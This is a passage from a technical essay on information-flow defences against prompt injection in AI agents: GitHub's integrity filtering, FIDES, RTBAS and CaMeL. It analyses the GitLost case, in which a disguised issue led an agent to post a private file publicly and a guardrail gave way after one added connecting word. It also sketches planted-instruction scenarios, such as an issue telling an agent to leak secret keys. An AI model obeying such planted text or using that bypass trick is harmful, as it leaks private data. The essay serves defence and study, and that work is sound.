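Since a run with a trusted start can still go wrong, GitHub also limits what the agent can do in any run. The agent's job has read-only permissions. To post a comment or open a pull request, the agent writes a description of the proposed action to a file. After the agent finishes, separate jobs with narrow write permissions carry out the proposals. The workflow's author must list each permitted kind of action in advance, and the runtime blocks the rest. GitHub calls the permitted actions safe outputs.

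Between the two stages, a second AI agent checks the proposed actions for leaked secrets, malicious code and policy violations. It has no write permissions and runs separately from the first agent, but by default it uses the same AI engine with a security-focused prompt. Because this check relies on a model's judgement, it has the weaknesses that adaptive attacks have exposed in other model-based checks. Workflow authors can add conventional scanners, including one that searches for credentials.

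A firewall restricts which internet domains the agent can reach, and a separate container holds the credentials for GitHub's tools. Like the hardened configuration that OpenClaw recommends, these limits reduce the damage an attacker can do but don't identify who influenced the model. They also share that configuration's weakness, because whoever steers the agent can still make it take any action the workflow permits. If the agent can post one public comment, an attacker may be able to choose its contents.

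### Filtering content by author

Integrity filtering controls what the agent reads. The agent gets its GitHub data through a gateway, a program that handles its tool calls. When a call returns issues or comments, the gateway assigns an integrity level to each item and removes any item below the workflow's minimum. GitHub defines five levels, from highest to lowest:

| Level | Content that qualifies |
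|---|---|
| merged | Merged pull requests, and commits in the project's default branch, whoever wrote them |
| approved | Content from owners, members and collaborators; pull requests from branches of the public repository itself; trusted bots; everything in private repositories |
| unapproved | Content from contributors and first-time contributors |
| none | Content from people with no recognised association, or who are new to GitHub |
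| blocked | Content from accounts on the workflow's blocklist |

A minimum of "approved" admits approved and merged content. A minimum of "none" admits everything except blocked content, which no setting can admit.

The levels are based on a person's relationship with the project, which only imperfectly indicates whether a particular text is safe. An experienced contributor's comment may contain a malicious line copied from elsewhere, and a newcomer's bug report is usually harmless. But an attacker can't raise an item's level by rewording it. *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group GitHub Next, argues against relying on filters that look for suspicious wording, because attackers can rephrase their text or split it across several fields.

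GitHub's *Weekly Update* (2026) reports that version 0.60.0, released on March 17, replaced an earlier automatic lockdown with a default minimum of "approved" for public repositories and "none" for private and internal ones. Public repositories that authenticated through a GitHub App, a kind of integration with its own credentials, were exempt from this default until a later GitHub update closed that gap.

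GitHub's agent keeps the same privileges throughout the run, unlike a process under the low-water mark, and the gateway withholds content the agent isn't supposed to trust. A stranger's comment therefore can't make a run useless for its original purpose, whereas it could under a rule that taints the whole context.

The disadvantage is that the agent may work from incomplete information. Suppose it searches for earlier reports of a bug, and the only ones came from outsiders. With a minimum of "approved", the search returns nothing and the agent may conclude that the bug is new. The gateway removes items without notifying the agent, but logs each removal with the author, the tool and the reason. Maintainers can check the log and lower the minimum if the agent misses too much.

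GitHub therefore suggests different minimums for different tasks. An agent that changes code should read only approved or merged content. A triage agent, which sorts incoming issues, can use "unapproved" because it is allowed fewer actions. Spam detection needs "none", and GitHub advises against applying its results without review. Agents that read less trusted content thus get weaker privileges, but the workflow's author sets both the minimum and the privileges before the run, and nothing adjusts them automatically.

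The filter also doesn't cover all the data an agent can read. GitHub Next describes support for data from outside GitHub as future work, so a web page from a permitted domain doesn't get an integrity level. The filter only partly covers GitHub data that a workflow collects with ordinary commands before the agent starts, for instance by saving issues to a file. A proxy applies the minimum level to these commands, but not the lists of blocked users, trusted users or special labels. If a maintainer has blocked an account but set the minimum to "none", such a command could still fetch that account's comments and put them where the agent will read them.

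### How overrides combine

A maintainer often wants the agent to read one outsider's issue without trusting everything that person writes. Workflow authors can choose approval labels, which are visible tags that people attach to issues on GitHub, such as "human-reviewed". An item with one of these labels counts as at least approved. They can also list trusted users, whose content all gets at least that level. Refusal labels lower an item to "none".

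Since version 0.68.2, workflows can also let maintainers change an item's level with emoji reactions. By default, a thumbs-up or heart from an owner, member or collaborator raises the item to "approved", and a thumbs-down or confused face lowers it to "none". The gateway ignores reactions from people below the required level, so reactions from many new accounts can't get a comment approved.

GitHub computes the effective level by applying the first rule that matches:

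1. If the author is blocked, the level is "blocked".
2. If the item has a refusal label, the level is "none".
3. If the author is a trusted user, the level is max(base, approved).
4. If the item has an approval label, the level is max(base, approved).
5. Otherwise, the item keeps its base level.

Taking the maximum ensures that an endorsement never lowers an item's level, so a merged pull request keeps its merged level. This list leaves out reactions. GitHub Next's account includes them and works in the opposite direction, starting from the base level and letting later steps override earlier ones. The steps cover trusted users, approval labels, endorsing reactions, disapproving reactions and blocked users, in that order. Disapproval therefore overrides all three kinds of promotion. In both accounts, any maintainer's objection overrides any endorsement, and blocking overrides everything.

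### An issue from a first-time contributor

Suppose Maya maintains a public repository, and Priya, whom GitHub classes as a first-time contributor, reports a bug there. Maya has one agent that writes fixes, with a minimum of "approved", and another that sorts incoming issues, with a minimum of "unapproved". She has turned reactions on and chosen "human-reviewed" as an approval label. The table shows the issue as the gateway would return it after each event.

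| Event | Effective level | Can the fixing agent read it? | Can the sorting agent read it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Priya opens the issue | unapproved | No | Yes |
| Another outside contributor adds a thumbs-up | unapproved | No | Yes |
| Maya adds the "human-reviewed" label | max(unapproved, approved) = approved | Yes | Yes |
| Tom, also a maintainer, adds a thumbs-down | none | No | No |
| Tom removes his reaction | approved | Yes | Yes |
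| Maya blocks Priya's account | blocked | No | No |

If GitHub had recorded no association between Priya and the project, the issue would have started at "none", and neither agent could have read it through the gateway until Maya approved it. The gateway also evaluates comments separately, so Maya's approval of the issue doesn't extend to a stranger's later reply.

Maya can endorse a single issue with one click by labeling it. But her endorsement is only as reliable as her reading of the issue, and it can go wrong in several ways.

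Maya may not see all of the issue's text, because its author can include HTML comments, which GitHub's web pages hide. When an issue triggers a workflow, GitHub's sanitiser converts these comments to plain text in parentheses and passes them to the model. An instruction Maya couldn't see in her browser could therefore reach the agent with her endorsement.

An issue's author can normally edit it after a maintainer endorses it, and neither of GitHub's two lists of rules withdraws the endorsement after an edit. If the label stays in place, Priya could rewrite an approved issue and the gateway would still treat it as approved. Negev did something similar to Ash when he added rules to a document that Ash had already saved. A safer rule would attach the endorsement to the exact version the maintainer read, so that any edit would require a new decision.

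The published rule checks whether an item has an approval label, not who added it. Adding labels normally requires some authority over the repository, so a stranger can't approve their own issue, but a sorting agent may have that authority. GitHub's guide recommends one called Repo Assist, which labels incoming issues and decides what reaches the agents that change code. GitHub Next's example of approval labels includes "triaged", a label such an agent would naturally apply. If Maya lets her sorting agent add it, Priya's untrusted text could lead it to approve her issue for the more powerful agent. To avoid this, Maya can reserve approval labels for people, or use reactions, for which the gateway checks the level of the account that reacted.

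GitHub Next also acknowledges that the whole system depends on the security of the maintainers' accounts. Someone who takes over Maya's account can write comments that the gateway will label as approved.

### The read and write rules

The five levels are a simplified form of decentralised information-flow control. In this model each agent and each piece of data has an integrity label and a secrecy (confidentiality) label, and each label is a set of tags. Write I for an integrity label and S for a secrecy label. GitHub Next's rules are then:

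| Operation | Integrity condition | Secrecy condition |
|---|---|---|
| The agent reads a resource | I(resource) ⊇ I(agent) | S(resource) ⊆ S(agent) |
| The agent writes to a resource | I(resource) ⊆ I(agent) | S(resource) ⊇ S(agent) |

An agent may read only data at least as trustworthy as its minimum, I(agent), and may write only to places that require no more trust than the agent has. For secrecy, an agent may read only what its own label covers, and may write only to places at least as restricted as the agent.

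Priya's issue illustrates the integrity condition. Because the levels are cumulative, unapproved content can have the label {unapproved} and approved content the label {unapproved, approved}. The fixing agent's minimum is {unapproved, approved}. Before Maya endorses the issue, its label is {unapproved}, which doesn't contain everything in the agent's minimum, so the read fails. After the endorsement, the label equals the minimum and the read succeeds.

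GitHub splits the work between two components. A guard written for a particular service assigns the tags, for instance marking a collaborator's comment as approved. A small reference monitor then compares the sets of tags without interpreting them. To add another service such as Slack, developers would write a new guard and leave the monitor unchanged. This separation makes the monitor easier to check, but the result still depends on the guard assigning the right tags. GitHub Next names FIDES, the agent design of Costa and colleagues, as a similar approach.

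GitHub also applies the levels to the memory that agents keep between runs. Without separation, a sorting agent that had read a stranger's issue could save a note that a fixing agent later relies on. GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* prevents this by giving each integrity level its own branch of the stored memory and allowing only runs at that level to write to it. The key to the stored memory includes a short code computed from the filtering policy, so the system can detect when a maintainer changes the policy.

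GitHub Next states in its article that the system tracks secrecy labels but doesn't yet use them to block anything, and that integrity filtering therefore can't prevent leaks between repositories.

### GitLost

In July 2026, Sasi Levi, a security researcher at Noma Labs, demonstrated such a leak. As Levi describes in *GitLost* (2026), assigning an issue started the workflow. The agent read the issue's title and text and posted a comment in reply. It also had read access to other repositories in the same organisation, including private ones.

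The researchers opened an issue in a public repository that looked like a sales executive's follow-up to a customer meeting. The issue included, among other questions, a request for the contents of a file in a private repository. After the issue was assigned, the agent fetched the file and posted its contents in a public comment. The attacker needed no access to the private repository and no technical skill. Levi reports that other triggers also worked.

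Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) reports that Noma ran the test on its own repositories and that the leaked file was a short placeholder. The test shows that the attack is possible under this configuration, but not how many organisations use a similar one.

mcp.directory's *GitLost* examined the workflow's public files and found that the configuration looked cautious. The workflow declared read-only permissions for its own repository and allowed one kind of output, a comment. Access to the private repository came from a separate token with a wider scope. That token was read-only as well, but the leak required only permission to read in one place and to write in another.

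#### Why the account check did not help

When a run starts with an assignment, the initiator is whoever assigned the issue. Levi describes an automation assigning it, but according to mcp.directory, the researchers assigned it themselves. In either case, an account with some standing in the repository started the run, and checking that account would have revealed nothing about the issue's author.

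A session-origin rule could have stopped the attack if it had treated the issue's author as the origin. A Hacker News commenter quoted by mcp.directory argued that the agent should have no permissions that the person addressing it lacks. Under that rule, an agent answering a stranger's issue could read only public repositories. The rule would be easy to apply here because the run had one main source of text, but harder to apply to a long discussion with many authors, where the system would have to combine their permissions.

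#### Whether integrity filtering was on

The compiled workflow contained a guard with a minimum integrity level, so filtering was configured. The file read the level from a variable that GitHub set when the run started. Under the default for public repositories, the level would have been "approved".

This doesn't settle whether the filter examined the issue that started the run. GitHub's reference describes the filter as acting on the results of tool calls, but the text of a triggering event can reach the prompt another way, through an earlier job that sanitises it and makes it available. The sanitiser disables mentions, removes links to untrusted domains, converts HTML and limits length. It doesn't check the author's integrity level, and a polite question in plain English would pass through unchanged.

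GitHub's maintenance guide, however, says that filtering removes content from untrusted users before the agent's context is assembled. Taken literally, that would include the triggering issue. But the same guide says that Repo Assist sees all incoming content, including issues from untrusted users, even though it runs at "unapproved", a level that excludes people with no association with the repository. The two statements can't both be true of the triggering issue. The simplest explanation is that the triggering text bypasses the gateway's filter. GitHub doesn't say so explicitly, but maintainers would be wise to assume that it does.

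If the researchers opened the issue from the repository owner's account, the filter would have rated it as approved, and the demonstration would not have tested how the filter handles a stranger's issue. The evidence doesn't support mcp.directory's claim that GitLost defeated integrity filtering, because the filter may never have examined the issue or may have admitted it correctly.

The private file would have passed the filter anyway, because everything in a private repository counts as approved. Integrity filtering is meant to keep untrustworthy text away from the agent, but the problem here was where the agent sent a trustworthy file.

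#### The guardrail that gave way

A guardrail blocked the request at first. Levi tried variations until he found that putting one connecting word before the question about the private file was enough to get an answer. He says the word led the model to reframe its output instead of refusing, and Expert Insights similarly explains that the word made the request look like part of an existing task. One of the attacks on prompt sandwiching that Nasr and colleagues collected used much the same trick.

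Accounts differ on which guardrail was bypassed. Expert Insights attributes the refusal to Copilot, but the workflow file that mcp.directory quotes specifies Claude Opus 4.6. mcp.directory attributes the bypass to the separate agent that checks proposed outputs. Levi's description fits the first model's own refusal better. The comment appeared in public, so any active output check also failed to stop it. A credential scanner would not have helped, because the file contained no credentials.

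#### What the secrecy rules would have done

GitHub's own label model would have blocked the leak if the system had enforced it. Call the private repository's tag p. The private file has the secrecy label {p}, and a public comment has the empty label ∅, because anyone may read it. The agent's label can either include p or leave it out:

| Secrecy label of the agent | Read the private file | Post a public comment |
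|---|---|---|
| ∅ | Blocked, because {p} is not a subset of ∅ | Allowed |
| {p} | Allowed | Blocked, because ∅ is not a superset of {p} |

Neither choice lets the agent do both. The rule doesn't depend on recognising the injection, so it would work however the attacker worded the request. In the compiled workflow, however, the guard on outputs accepted data with any label. It limited the agent to posting a comment but didn't restrict where the comment's contents came from.

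A strict rule would also block legitimate work. A company might want an agent to read a private repository and publish release notes from it. To allow this, someone with the authority to declassify the notes would have to review them before publication or exempt the workflow in advance.

#### Responsibility and GitHub's response

Several developers objected to calling GitLost a vulnerability in GitHub, because the researchers had created a token with access to private repositories and given it to an agent that answered public issues. GitHub's documentation already advised people to give access only to the repositories they need. mcp.directory considers this criticism technically fair but replies that a demonstration has to set up the conditions it is testing, and that some real organisations probably use one broad token for convenience.

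Both points are reasonable. The token made the leak possible, and a token for a single repository would have prevented it. Workflow authors can also use the gateway to restrict the agent to named repositories, but by default the agent can access every repository the token can reach. However, the product offered labels for tracking private data yet still allowed that data into a public comment, so the owner's configuration was the only dependable protection.

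Noma told GitHub about the problem before publishing. The Next Web's *GitLost* reports that Noma proposed a documentation note about the risk of sharing keys between repositories, that GitHub had not added it by early July, and that GitHub didn't respond to questions from The Register, a technology news site. Kiteworks' *GitHub's AI Agent Leaked Private Code With One Word* reports that GitHub later updated its documentation, but that Noma considers the underlying design flaw unresolved. SecurityWeek's *Critical Vulnerability Exposes GitHub Agentic Workflows to Prompt Injection* reports that Noma advises organisations to treat all user-controlled content as untrusted, give agents as few permissions as possible, restrict what they can post publicly and sanitise what they read. Limiting permissions and restricting public posts would have stopped the GitLost leak. Sanitising is much less dependable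 against a request written in ordinary language.

On July 12, six days after Levi's post, GitHub merged a change that lets workflow authors turn off two controls already defined in the gateway's specification by writing "private-to-public-flows: allow" in a workflow's settings. Judging by their names, "forcePublicRepos" limits an agent to public repositories, and the "sink visibility" check compares the source of data with the visibility of its destination. The opt-out also suggests that these controls apply by default in at least some workflows. GitHub Next's statement that the system only tracks secrecy is therefore probably out of date, although some public workflows may still lack this protection.

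The opt-out is a form of declassification that the workflow's author grants before the agent has read anything. That suits a workflow that only publishes release notes, but the opt-out would also cover anything a stranger later persuades the agent to publish. A check that distinguishes only between public and private would still let an agent copy text from one private repository into another with different readers. GitHub's secrecy tags identify individual repositories, so the gateway could also block such copying if it enforced the full read and write rules.

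## FIDES: labels that follow data through a session

GitHub's filter withholds untrusted text from an agent, which only works if the agent can do its job without that text. Costa and colleagues at Microsoft designed FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System) to let an agent work with such text while tracking where it goes. In FIDES, a session's origin determines only its first label. The researchers normally label the developer's instructions and the user's messages as trusted and public, but a runtime could give a less trusted label to a session opened by a stranger's email. After that, the label depends on what enters the session.

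### The basic planner

FIDES builds on a simpler design. A planner is the part of the runtime that decides, after each message, whether to query the model, run a tool or finish. The basic planner stores the conversation with a single label, L, for all of it. When a message m arrives, the planner combines the message's label with L:

L ← L ⊔ ℓ(m)

The model then receives the whole conversation, and its reply takes the label L. If the reply requests a tool, the call and all its arguments take L as well. The tool's result gets the label

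ℓ(result) = L ⊔ ℓ(arguments) ⊔ ℓ(data the tool read)

and so does anything the tool wrote. Untrusted text therefore can't become trusted by passing through a file.

In one AgentDojo task, the agent must check the reviews of a Paris hotel and book it for certain dates if its rating is above 4. The table shows the integrity label at each step of this task, with Maya as the user.

| Message | Its label | Session label afterwards | May the agent act? |
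|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Maya makes the request | T | T | Yes |
| 2. The model asks for the reviews | T | T | Yes |
| 3. The tool returns reviews that strangers wrote | U | T ⊔ U = U | No |
| 4. The model asks to book the hotel | U | U | No, so the runtime blocks the booking |

The reviews may be honest, and the booking is what Maya asked for. If she now writes "Yes, book it", her message is trusted, but the next call also fails because U ⊔ T is still U. No later message can turn U back into T, so she has to approve the call separately or start a new session. Label creep also occurred in older systems, but an agent can reach this point with its first tool call.

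### Hidden variables

FIDES avoids this by keeping untrusted results out of the conversation. When a tool returns something, FIDES compares each part's label with L. If a part would make L more restrictive, FIDES stores it in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name. The model reads everything else, and L doesn't change. In a list of bank transactions, for example, the model might see the dates and amounts but only a variable name in place of each description.

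The model can use a variable without reading it by passing its name to a tool. FIDES inserts the contents just before the tool runs. Suppose Maya asks the agent to send her three latest emails to Tom on Slack. The model can choose both tools and the recipient without reading any of the emails, so the call and the recipient are trusted. The message body keeps its untrusted label, and a policy can accept that combination.

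Some tasks require a model to read the hidden text, such as summarising the emails before sending them. FIDES passes the question and the variables to an isolated model with no tools, and stores the answer in another variable with the combined label. Simon Willison proposed this division of work in 2023 as the Dual LLM pattern. FIDES differs in hiding only the data that would change the session's label. An injection can still mislead the isolated model, perhaps into writing an empty summary, but it can't make that model call a tool.

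The model can still learn some things about text that is hidden from it. In one example run from Costa and colleagues, the user asks the agent to find the Slack channel with the fewest messages and add Alice to it. The model doesn't read any messages, but it can count the variables that stand for them. Anyone who can post in those channels can change the count and so influence which channel Alice joins. The labels don't capture this influence because the lists are marked as trusted even though their entries are not.

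### Answers restricted to a few values

The planning model can't complete the hotel task with variables alone, because it has to learn whether the rating is above 4. Costa and colleagues call a task data dependent if no single sequence of tool calls would solve it for all possible data. The planning model could open the variable that holds the reviews, but the session would then become untrusted, as it did under the basic planner.

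The planner can instead ask the isolated model a yes-or-no question. Constrained decoding, which prevents a model from generating tokens that break a required format, limits the answer to true or false. FIDES adds the format to the label, so the answer is labeled (U, bool). It ranks formats by how much information they can carry: at most one bit for a yes-or-no answer, at most log₂ k bits for a choice among k options, and no fixed limit for free text.

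| Step | What the planning model reads | Session label |
|---|---|---|
| Maya makes the request | Her request | T |
| The tool returns the reviews | The name of a variable | T |
| The isolated model answers whether the rating is above 4 | The name of a second variable | T |
| The planner opens the second variable | "true" | U, yes-or-no only |
| The model asks to book the hotel | – | U, yes-or-no only; the booking succeeds if the policy accepts such answers |

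Accepting the answer is a form of endorsement. A dishonest reviewer might fool the isolated model, but that would only lead to a booking at the hotel Maya named, on the dates she chose. If the planning model had read the reviews itself, the reviewer could have tried to make it do anything its tools allow.

One bit can still matter a great deal, since a wrong answer about whether an invoice is genuine may release a payment. The labels also don't record how many answers the planner has read. Combining two yes-or-no labels gives another yes-or-no label, so twenty answers may carry twenty bits while the label stays the same. Anyone writing a policy that accepts restricted answers should therefore consider what each question decides and how many questions the planner may ask.

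### The policies and the formal guarantee

For their tests, Costa and colleagues relaxed the two policies from the inbox example, on trusted calls and permitted readers, and assigned each tool one of three rules.

| Examples of tools | Condition for running the tool |
|---|---|
| Send money, book a hotel, change a password | The call comes from a trusted context |
| Send an email or a Slack message | The recipients may read the data and the message contains no untrusted link; otherwise, the call must come from a trusted context |
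| Add people to a calendar event | The participants may read the data, there is no untrusted link, and the call comes from a trusted context |

The first rule ignores the labels of arguments, which makes hidden variables much more useful but also allows calls with untrusted arguments. Suppose Maya asks the agent to pay a bill, and the isolated model extracts the account number from it. A planted line in the bill could make that model return an attacker's account number. The rule would still allow the payment, because the planning model requested it in a trusted context. Under the second rule, a planted instruction can make the agent send email, but only to people already allowed to read its contents.

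The formal guarantee concerns explicit secrecy, which is a property of one particular sequence of steps. If two data stores contain the same public data, they must still contain the same public data as each other after applying those steps to both. This means the steps may not copy secret data to a public place.

This doesn't cover implicit flows. If the agent posts "closed today" on a public page only when Maya's private calendar is empty, readers learn something about her calendar, even though the agent copied nothing from it. Costa and colleagues accept this because noninterference, the stricter standard, would in practice forbid almost any public action after the agent had read private data.

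Explicit secrecy is about confidentiality. For integrity, the basic planner gives the same protection as the low-water mark, since the agent can act only before untrusted text arrives. With hidden variables, that protection still covers the choice of tool call, but only if outsiders can't influence anything else the planning model reads, such as the length of a list.

### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested the planners with GPT-4o against an attack in which the planted text refers to the agent's tools by name. Without policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against the basic planner and 21 against FIDES. A simple filter that asked the model at the start to remove unneeded tools allowed 20. With policy checks, none succeeded against either planner. The researchers excluded some cases that the benchmark counted as successes, including actions the policies allowed and planted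 text that only changed the wording of an answer.

The protection therefore comes from the policy checks, and hidden variables mainly help the agent complete more tasks under those checks. The result of zero also depends on favourable labelling. AgentDojo has no labels, so the researchers treated a field as untrusted if the benchmark ever places an injection there. Someone deploying an agent would have to label its data without knowing where attacks will appear.

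The next table shows the share of tasks completed without an attack, using OpenAI's o1 model.

| Setting | Basic planner, no checks | Basic planner with checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office workspace | 70.0% | 48.0% | 64.5% |
| Travel | 82.0% | 75.0% | 68.0% |
| Banking | 96.2% | 37.5% | 56.2% |
| Slack | 87.6% | 17.1% | 54.3% |

Averaged across the four settings, the unprotected agent completed 84 percent of tasks, the basic planner with checks 44 percent and FIDES 61 percent. FIDES therefore recovered less than half of the drop caused by the checks. With GPT-4o, it beat the basic planner by only 8 points, because the model often confused variable names or failed to use the isolated model when needed. The basic planner did better in the travel setting, where many tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context and hidden variables only made the tasks harder.

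Both models are now old, and newer ones would probably handle the variables better. But they couldn't close the whole gap, because the policies are meant to block some of the tasks. Many banking tasks, for instance, ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. Restricted answers might help with some of these, but the researchers didn't test constrained decoding.

One of the successes shows that the system's protection depends on how data is labeled. The user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. The model saw the amounts and dates but not the hidden descriptions, judged a large transaction suspicious, and changed the password. The session stayed trusted throughout. But a payment's sender chooses the amount, so an outsider could influence this decision through a field labeled as trusted.

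When a check fails, the agent can ask the user for approval instead of abandoning the task. Kolluri and colleagues found that, at the same rate of task completion, checking labels first reduced approvals by a factor of 1.5 to 2.6 compared with an agent without labels. Their planner, Prudentia, builds on the FIDES code and makes the model aware of the policies so that it can look for a permitted way to do the task.

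### Keeping only the labels that mattered

Often only part of the conversation influences a reply. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, proposed keeping only the labels of documents that the answer needed. With two labels, trusted and untrusted, the method works as follows:

1. The model produces an answer y from the full context C.
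2. The system removes the untrusted documents, leaving C′, and tests whether y is still a likely answer. The condition is perplexity(y | C′) − perplexity(y | C) ≤ λ, where perplexity measures how unexpected a text is to the model and λ is a tolerance set in advance.
3. If the condition holds, the model answers again from C′ alone. The system discards y and returns the new answer, y′, with a trusted label.

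The third step makes the method safe because y′ comes from a context without any untrusted documents. If the estimate in the second step is wrong, or an attacker manipulates it, the answer may get worse, but untrusted content can't get a trusted label. An attacker can still add distracting text that changes y, so that the condition fails and the answer keeps its untrusted label.

The method also doesn't help with tasks that need the untrusted text. Maya's agent can't decide about the hotel without the reviews. In a test with pairs of news articles, the untrusted article was unnecessary for only 647 of 3,465 questions. The smaller of two Llama 2 models improved the label for 57 percent of those 647. The method did better on 40 invented conversations with search tools. The untrusted result was unnecessary in 20 of them, and the system improved the label in at least 17 of those 20.

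With two labels, this method adds one check and a second answer. With many unordered labels, such as a different set of readers for each document, the number of model calls can grow exponentially with the number of documents. FIDES could use this method instead of labelling replies cautiously, but Costa and colleagues left it out for simplicity.

*GIF* (2026) instead measures how much each passage affects the output. It slightly changes the numbers that represent the passage inside the model and measures how far the output distribution shifts. If the shift is small, little information flowed from the passage, and a policy can ignore that flow. This guarantee covers only small changes to the passage the model received, whereas noninterference would have to hold for every text an attacker could have written. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* still lists separating the influence of different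 sources inside a model as an open research challenge.

### RTBAS: screening, redaction and confirmation

In *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025), a screener marks the parts of the conversation that the model needs before it takes each step. The system combines the labels of those parts and removes everything whose label is more restrictive than the combined one. The model works from what remains, and if its tool call violates the policy, the system asks the user to confirm.

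The researchers built two screeners. One is a second language model that acts as a judge. The other is a small neural network that uses attention scores, which indicate how strongly each part of the input affected a draft of the output. This network classified 81 percent of its test examples correctly.

Zhong and colleagues argue that these mistakes can't compromise security. If the screener wrongly leaves out the stranger's email, the model doesn't see it. If it wrongly includes the email, the label becomes untrusted and the user has to confirm any sensitive call. The screener is much like Siddiqui's influence estimate in this respect.

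With only two integrity labels, though, marking even one web page as relevant makes the combined label untrusted. There is then no reason to remove any other untrusted text, so the stranger's email returns to the context along with the web page. More detailed labels would reduce this problem.

On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policy. It did not track one other attack, because the planted text was in material the user had written, which the system labelled as trusted. Without attacks, the share of tasks completed fell by 10 percent with the judge and 7.4 percent with the attention screener. The drop was worst on Slack, where the agent completed 22 percent of tasks with the judge and 33 percent with the attention screener. Many Slack tasks involve reading a website and acting on it, and Zhong and colleagues think these should require confirmation anyway.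 On the banking tasks, the screeners roughly doubled the running time and the price.

In the AgentDojo tests, the system skipped calls that needed confirmation instead of requesting it. Real users could approve some of those calls and let the tasks finish, but they could also approve an attack. In a separate test of 37 cases involving private data, RTBAS requested unnecessary confirmation in 8 percent of cases with the judge and 16 percent with the attention screener, compared with 30 percent when every call required confirmation.

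### Steps that depend on a model's judgement

All these designs use models in several places. Some of the models' mistakes only make the agent less useful, while others let an outsider bypass the policy.

| Step | Possible result of a mistake | Does the label guarantee still hold? |
|---|---|---|
| The planning model chooses a tool call | It requests a harmful action, and the runtime checks the call | Yes |
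| The isolated model writes free text | The text is false but stays untrusted | Yes, but the text can do harm if the policy ignores argument labels |
| The isolated model gives a yes-or-no answer that the policy accepts | An attacker chooses the answer | Not for that choice |
| Siddiqui's method estimates influence | The answer is worse, or its label stays untrusted | Yes, because the model answers again without the removed text |
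| The RTBAS screener marks relevant text | The model lacks information, or the user gets an unnecessary question | Yes, because the system removes text above the chosen label |
| A classifier declares a document safe and raises its label | Planted instructions become trusted | No |

The last row comes from Costa and colleagues, who suggest that a system might upgrade a document's label after an injection detector has examined it. They warn against weakening the guarantee too far in this way. Attackers can adapt to detectors, so such an upgrade would let them get a trusted label by rewording their text.

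Siddiqui and colleagues also tested the shortcut of asking the model which documents influenced its answer. On the invented conversations, the larger Llama 2 model improved the label this way in 80 percent of the cases where improvement was possible. But if a system accepts the model's report without regenerating the answer, there is no guarantee that the removed label was irrelevant.

### FIDES in Microsoft's agent software

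Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced FIDES as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents. FIDES is included in the core Python package from version 1.3.0. It labels data as trusted or untrusted, and as public, private or "user identity", which covers the most sensitive personal information. Once a developer turns it on, FIDES by default hides untrusted results in variables and sends questions about them to an isolated model.

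The announcement describes an agent that sorts GitHub issues. An attacker files an issue instructing it to read a file of secret keys and post the contents as a comment. If the developer turns hiding off, the planning model reads this instruction and may follow it. The runtime lets the agent read the file but labels the contents private, so the session becomes both untrusted and private. The commenting tool accepts only public data, so the runtime blocks the comment or asks a person to approve it. The same kind of check would have stopped the GitLost leak. The attacker can still cause some disruption, because after reading the keys the agent can't post even a harmless comment in that run without approval.

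Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a simpler version in GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent. This version, available through an experimental setting, keeps one label for the whole context, like the basic planner. It enforced policies for only some of GitHub's tools and didn't yet support tools from other servers. Microsoft also released a gateway that can add labels and policies to existing tools.

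Label creep remains a problem in Agent Framework. When hiding is off, one untrusted issue makes the rest of the run untrusted unless the developer removes the issue from the context. Microsoft was considering letting labels decay when the runtime shortens a long conversation. Under Denning's rule, this would be unsafe if the shortened conversation included a summary of the issue.

### Data without a label

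The most serious weakness reported in Microsoft's announcement is that "a tool you forget to label is treated as trusted/public." If the developer in the GitHub example forgets to label the tool that reads issues, the attacker's text counts as trusted, and the agent can use it to overwrite files in the repository. The check on private data would still prevent the agent from posting the secret keys, unless the developer also forgot to label the tool that reads files.

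*Flowsh* (2026), a command shell for agents that tracks labels across commands and sessions, instead lets the user choose a default label for unlabelled files.

| Design | Treatment of data without a label |
|---|---|
| Siddiqui and colleagues | They recommend the most restrictive label |
| RTBAS | Trusted and public |
| *Flowsh* | The default in the configuration, for files |
| Agent Framework, May 2026 | Trusted and public |

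A permissive default lets developers add FIDES to an existing agent without labelling every tool first. Microsoft asked for feedback on whether tools without a label should instead count as untrusted. It also suggested deriving labels from tools' existing descriptions. Results from a tool that reaches the open internet would be untrusted, and results from a tool that requires a login would be private. This would save developers much of the labelling work, but it relies on tool authors describing their tools correctly.

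A developer who forgot a label would probably notice during the first test if unlabeled data were untrusted by default, because the agent would read it and then be unable to act. If the default is trusted, the agent keeps working normally, and the developer may not discover the missing label until an attack succeeds.

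## CaMeL: fixing the plan before untrusted content is read

FIDES chooses one tool call at a time, so some information about hidden data, such as the length of a list, can reach its planner. CaMeL (short for Capabilities for Machine Learning) has a model write the entire plan, as a program, before the agent reads any data. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). CaMeL combines the two kinds of rule. The program depends only on the request that opened the session, and every value it handles carries a record of its sources.

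### Two models and a controller

Like FIDES, CaMeL builds on the design Willison (2023) proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. A privileged model receives the user's requests and can call tools, while a quarantined model without tools reads the untrusted text. Willison assumes that an attacker may take over the quarantined model at any moment. A controller, an ordinary program, runs the tools and gives the privileged model variable names in place of untrusted results.

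Willison's one exception lets the quarantined model pass back a choice from a fixed set of categories, because the controller can check that the answer is one of them. This is much like the restricted answers in FIDES.

Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and any mistake that passes untrusted text to the privileged model undoes the protection. The CaMeL paper also found that the solution protects the choice of tools but not the values the agent passes to them, which Willison (2025) acknowledged in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*.

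### Sending Bob a document

The paper's example is a request to send Bob the document he asked for at the last meeting. Bob's address and the name of the document are both in the meeting notes. With Maya as the user, the privileged model might write this program:

```
notes    = find_file("notes from the last meeting with Bob")
address  = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's email address", notes, format = email address)
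title    = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes, format = text)
document = get_file(title)
send_email(to = address, subject = "The document you asked for", attachment = document)
```

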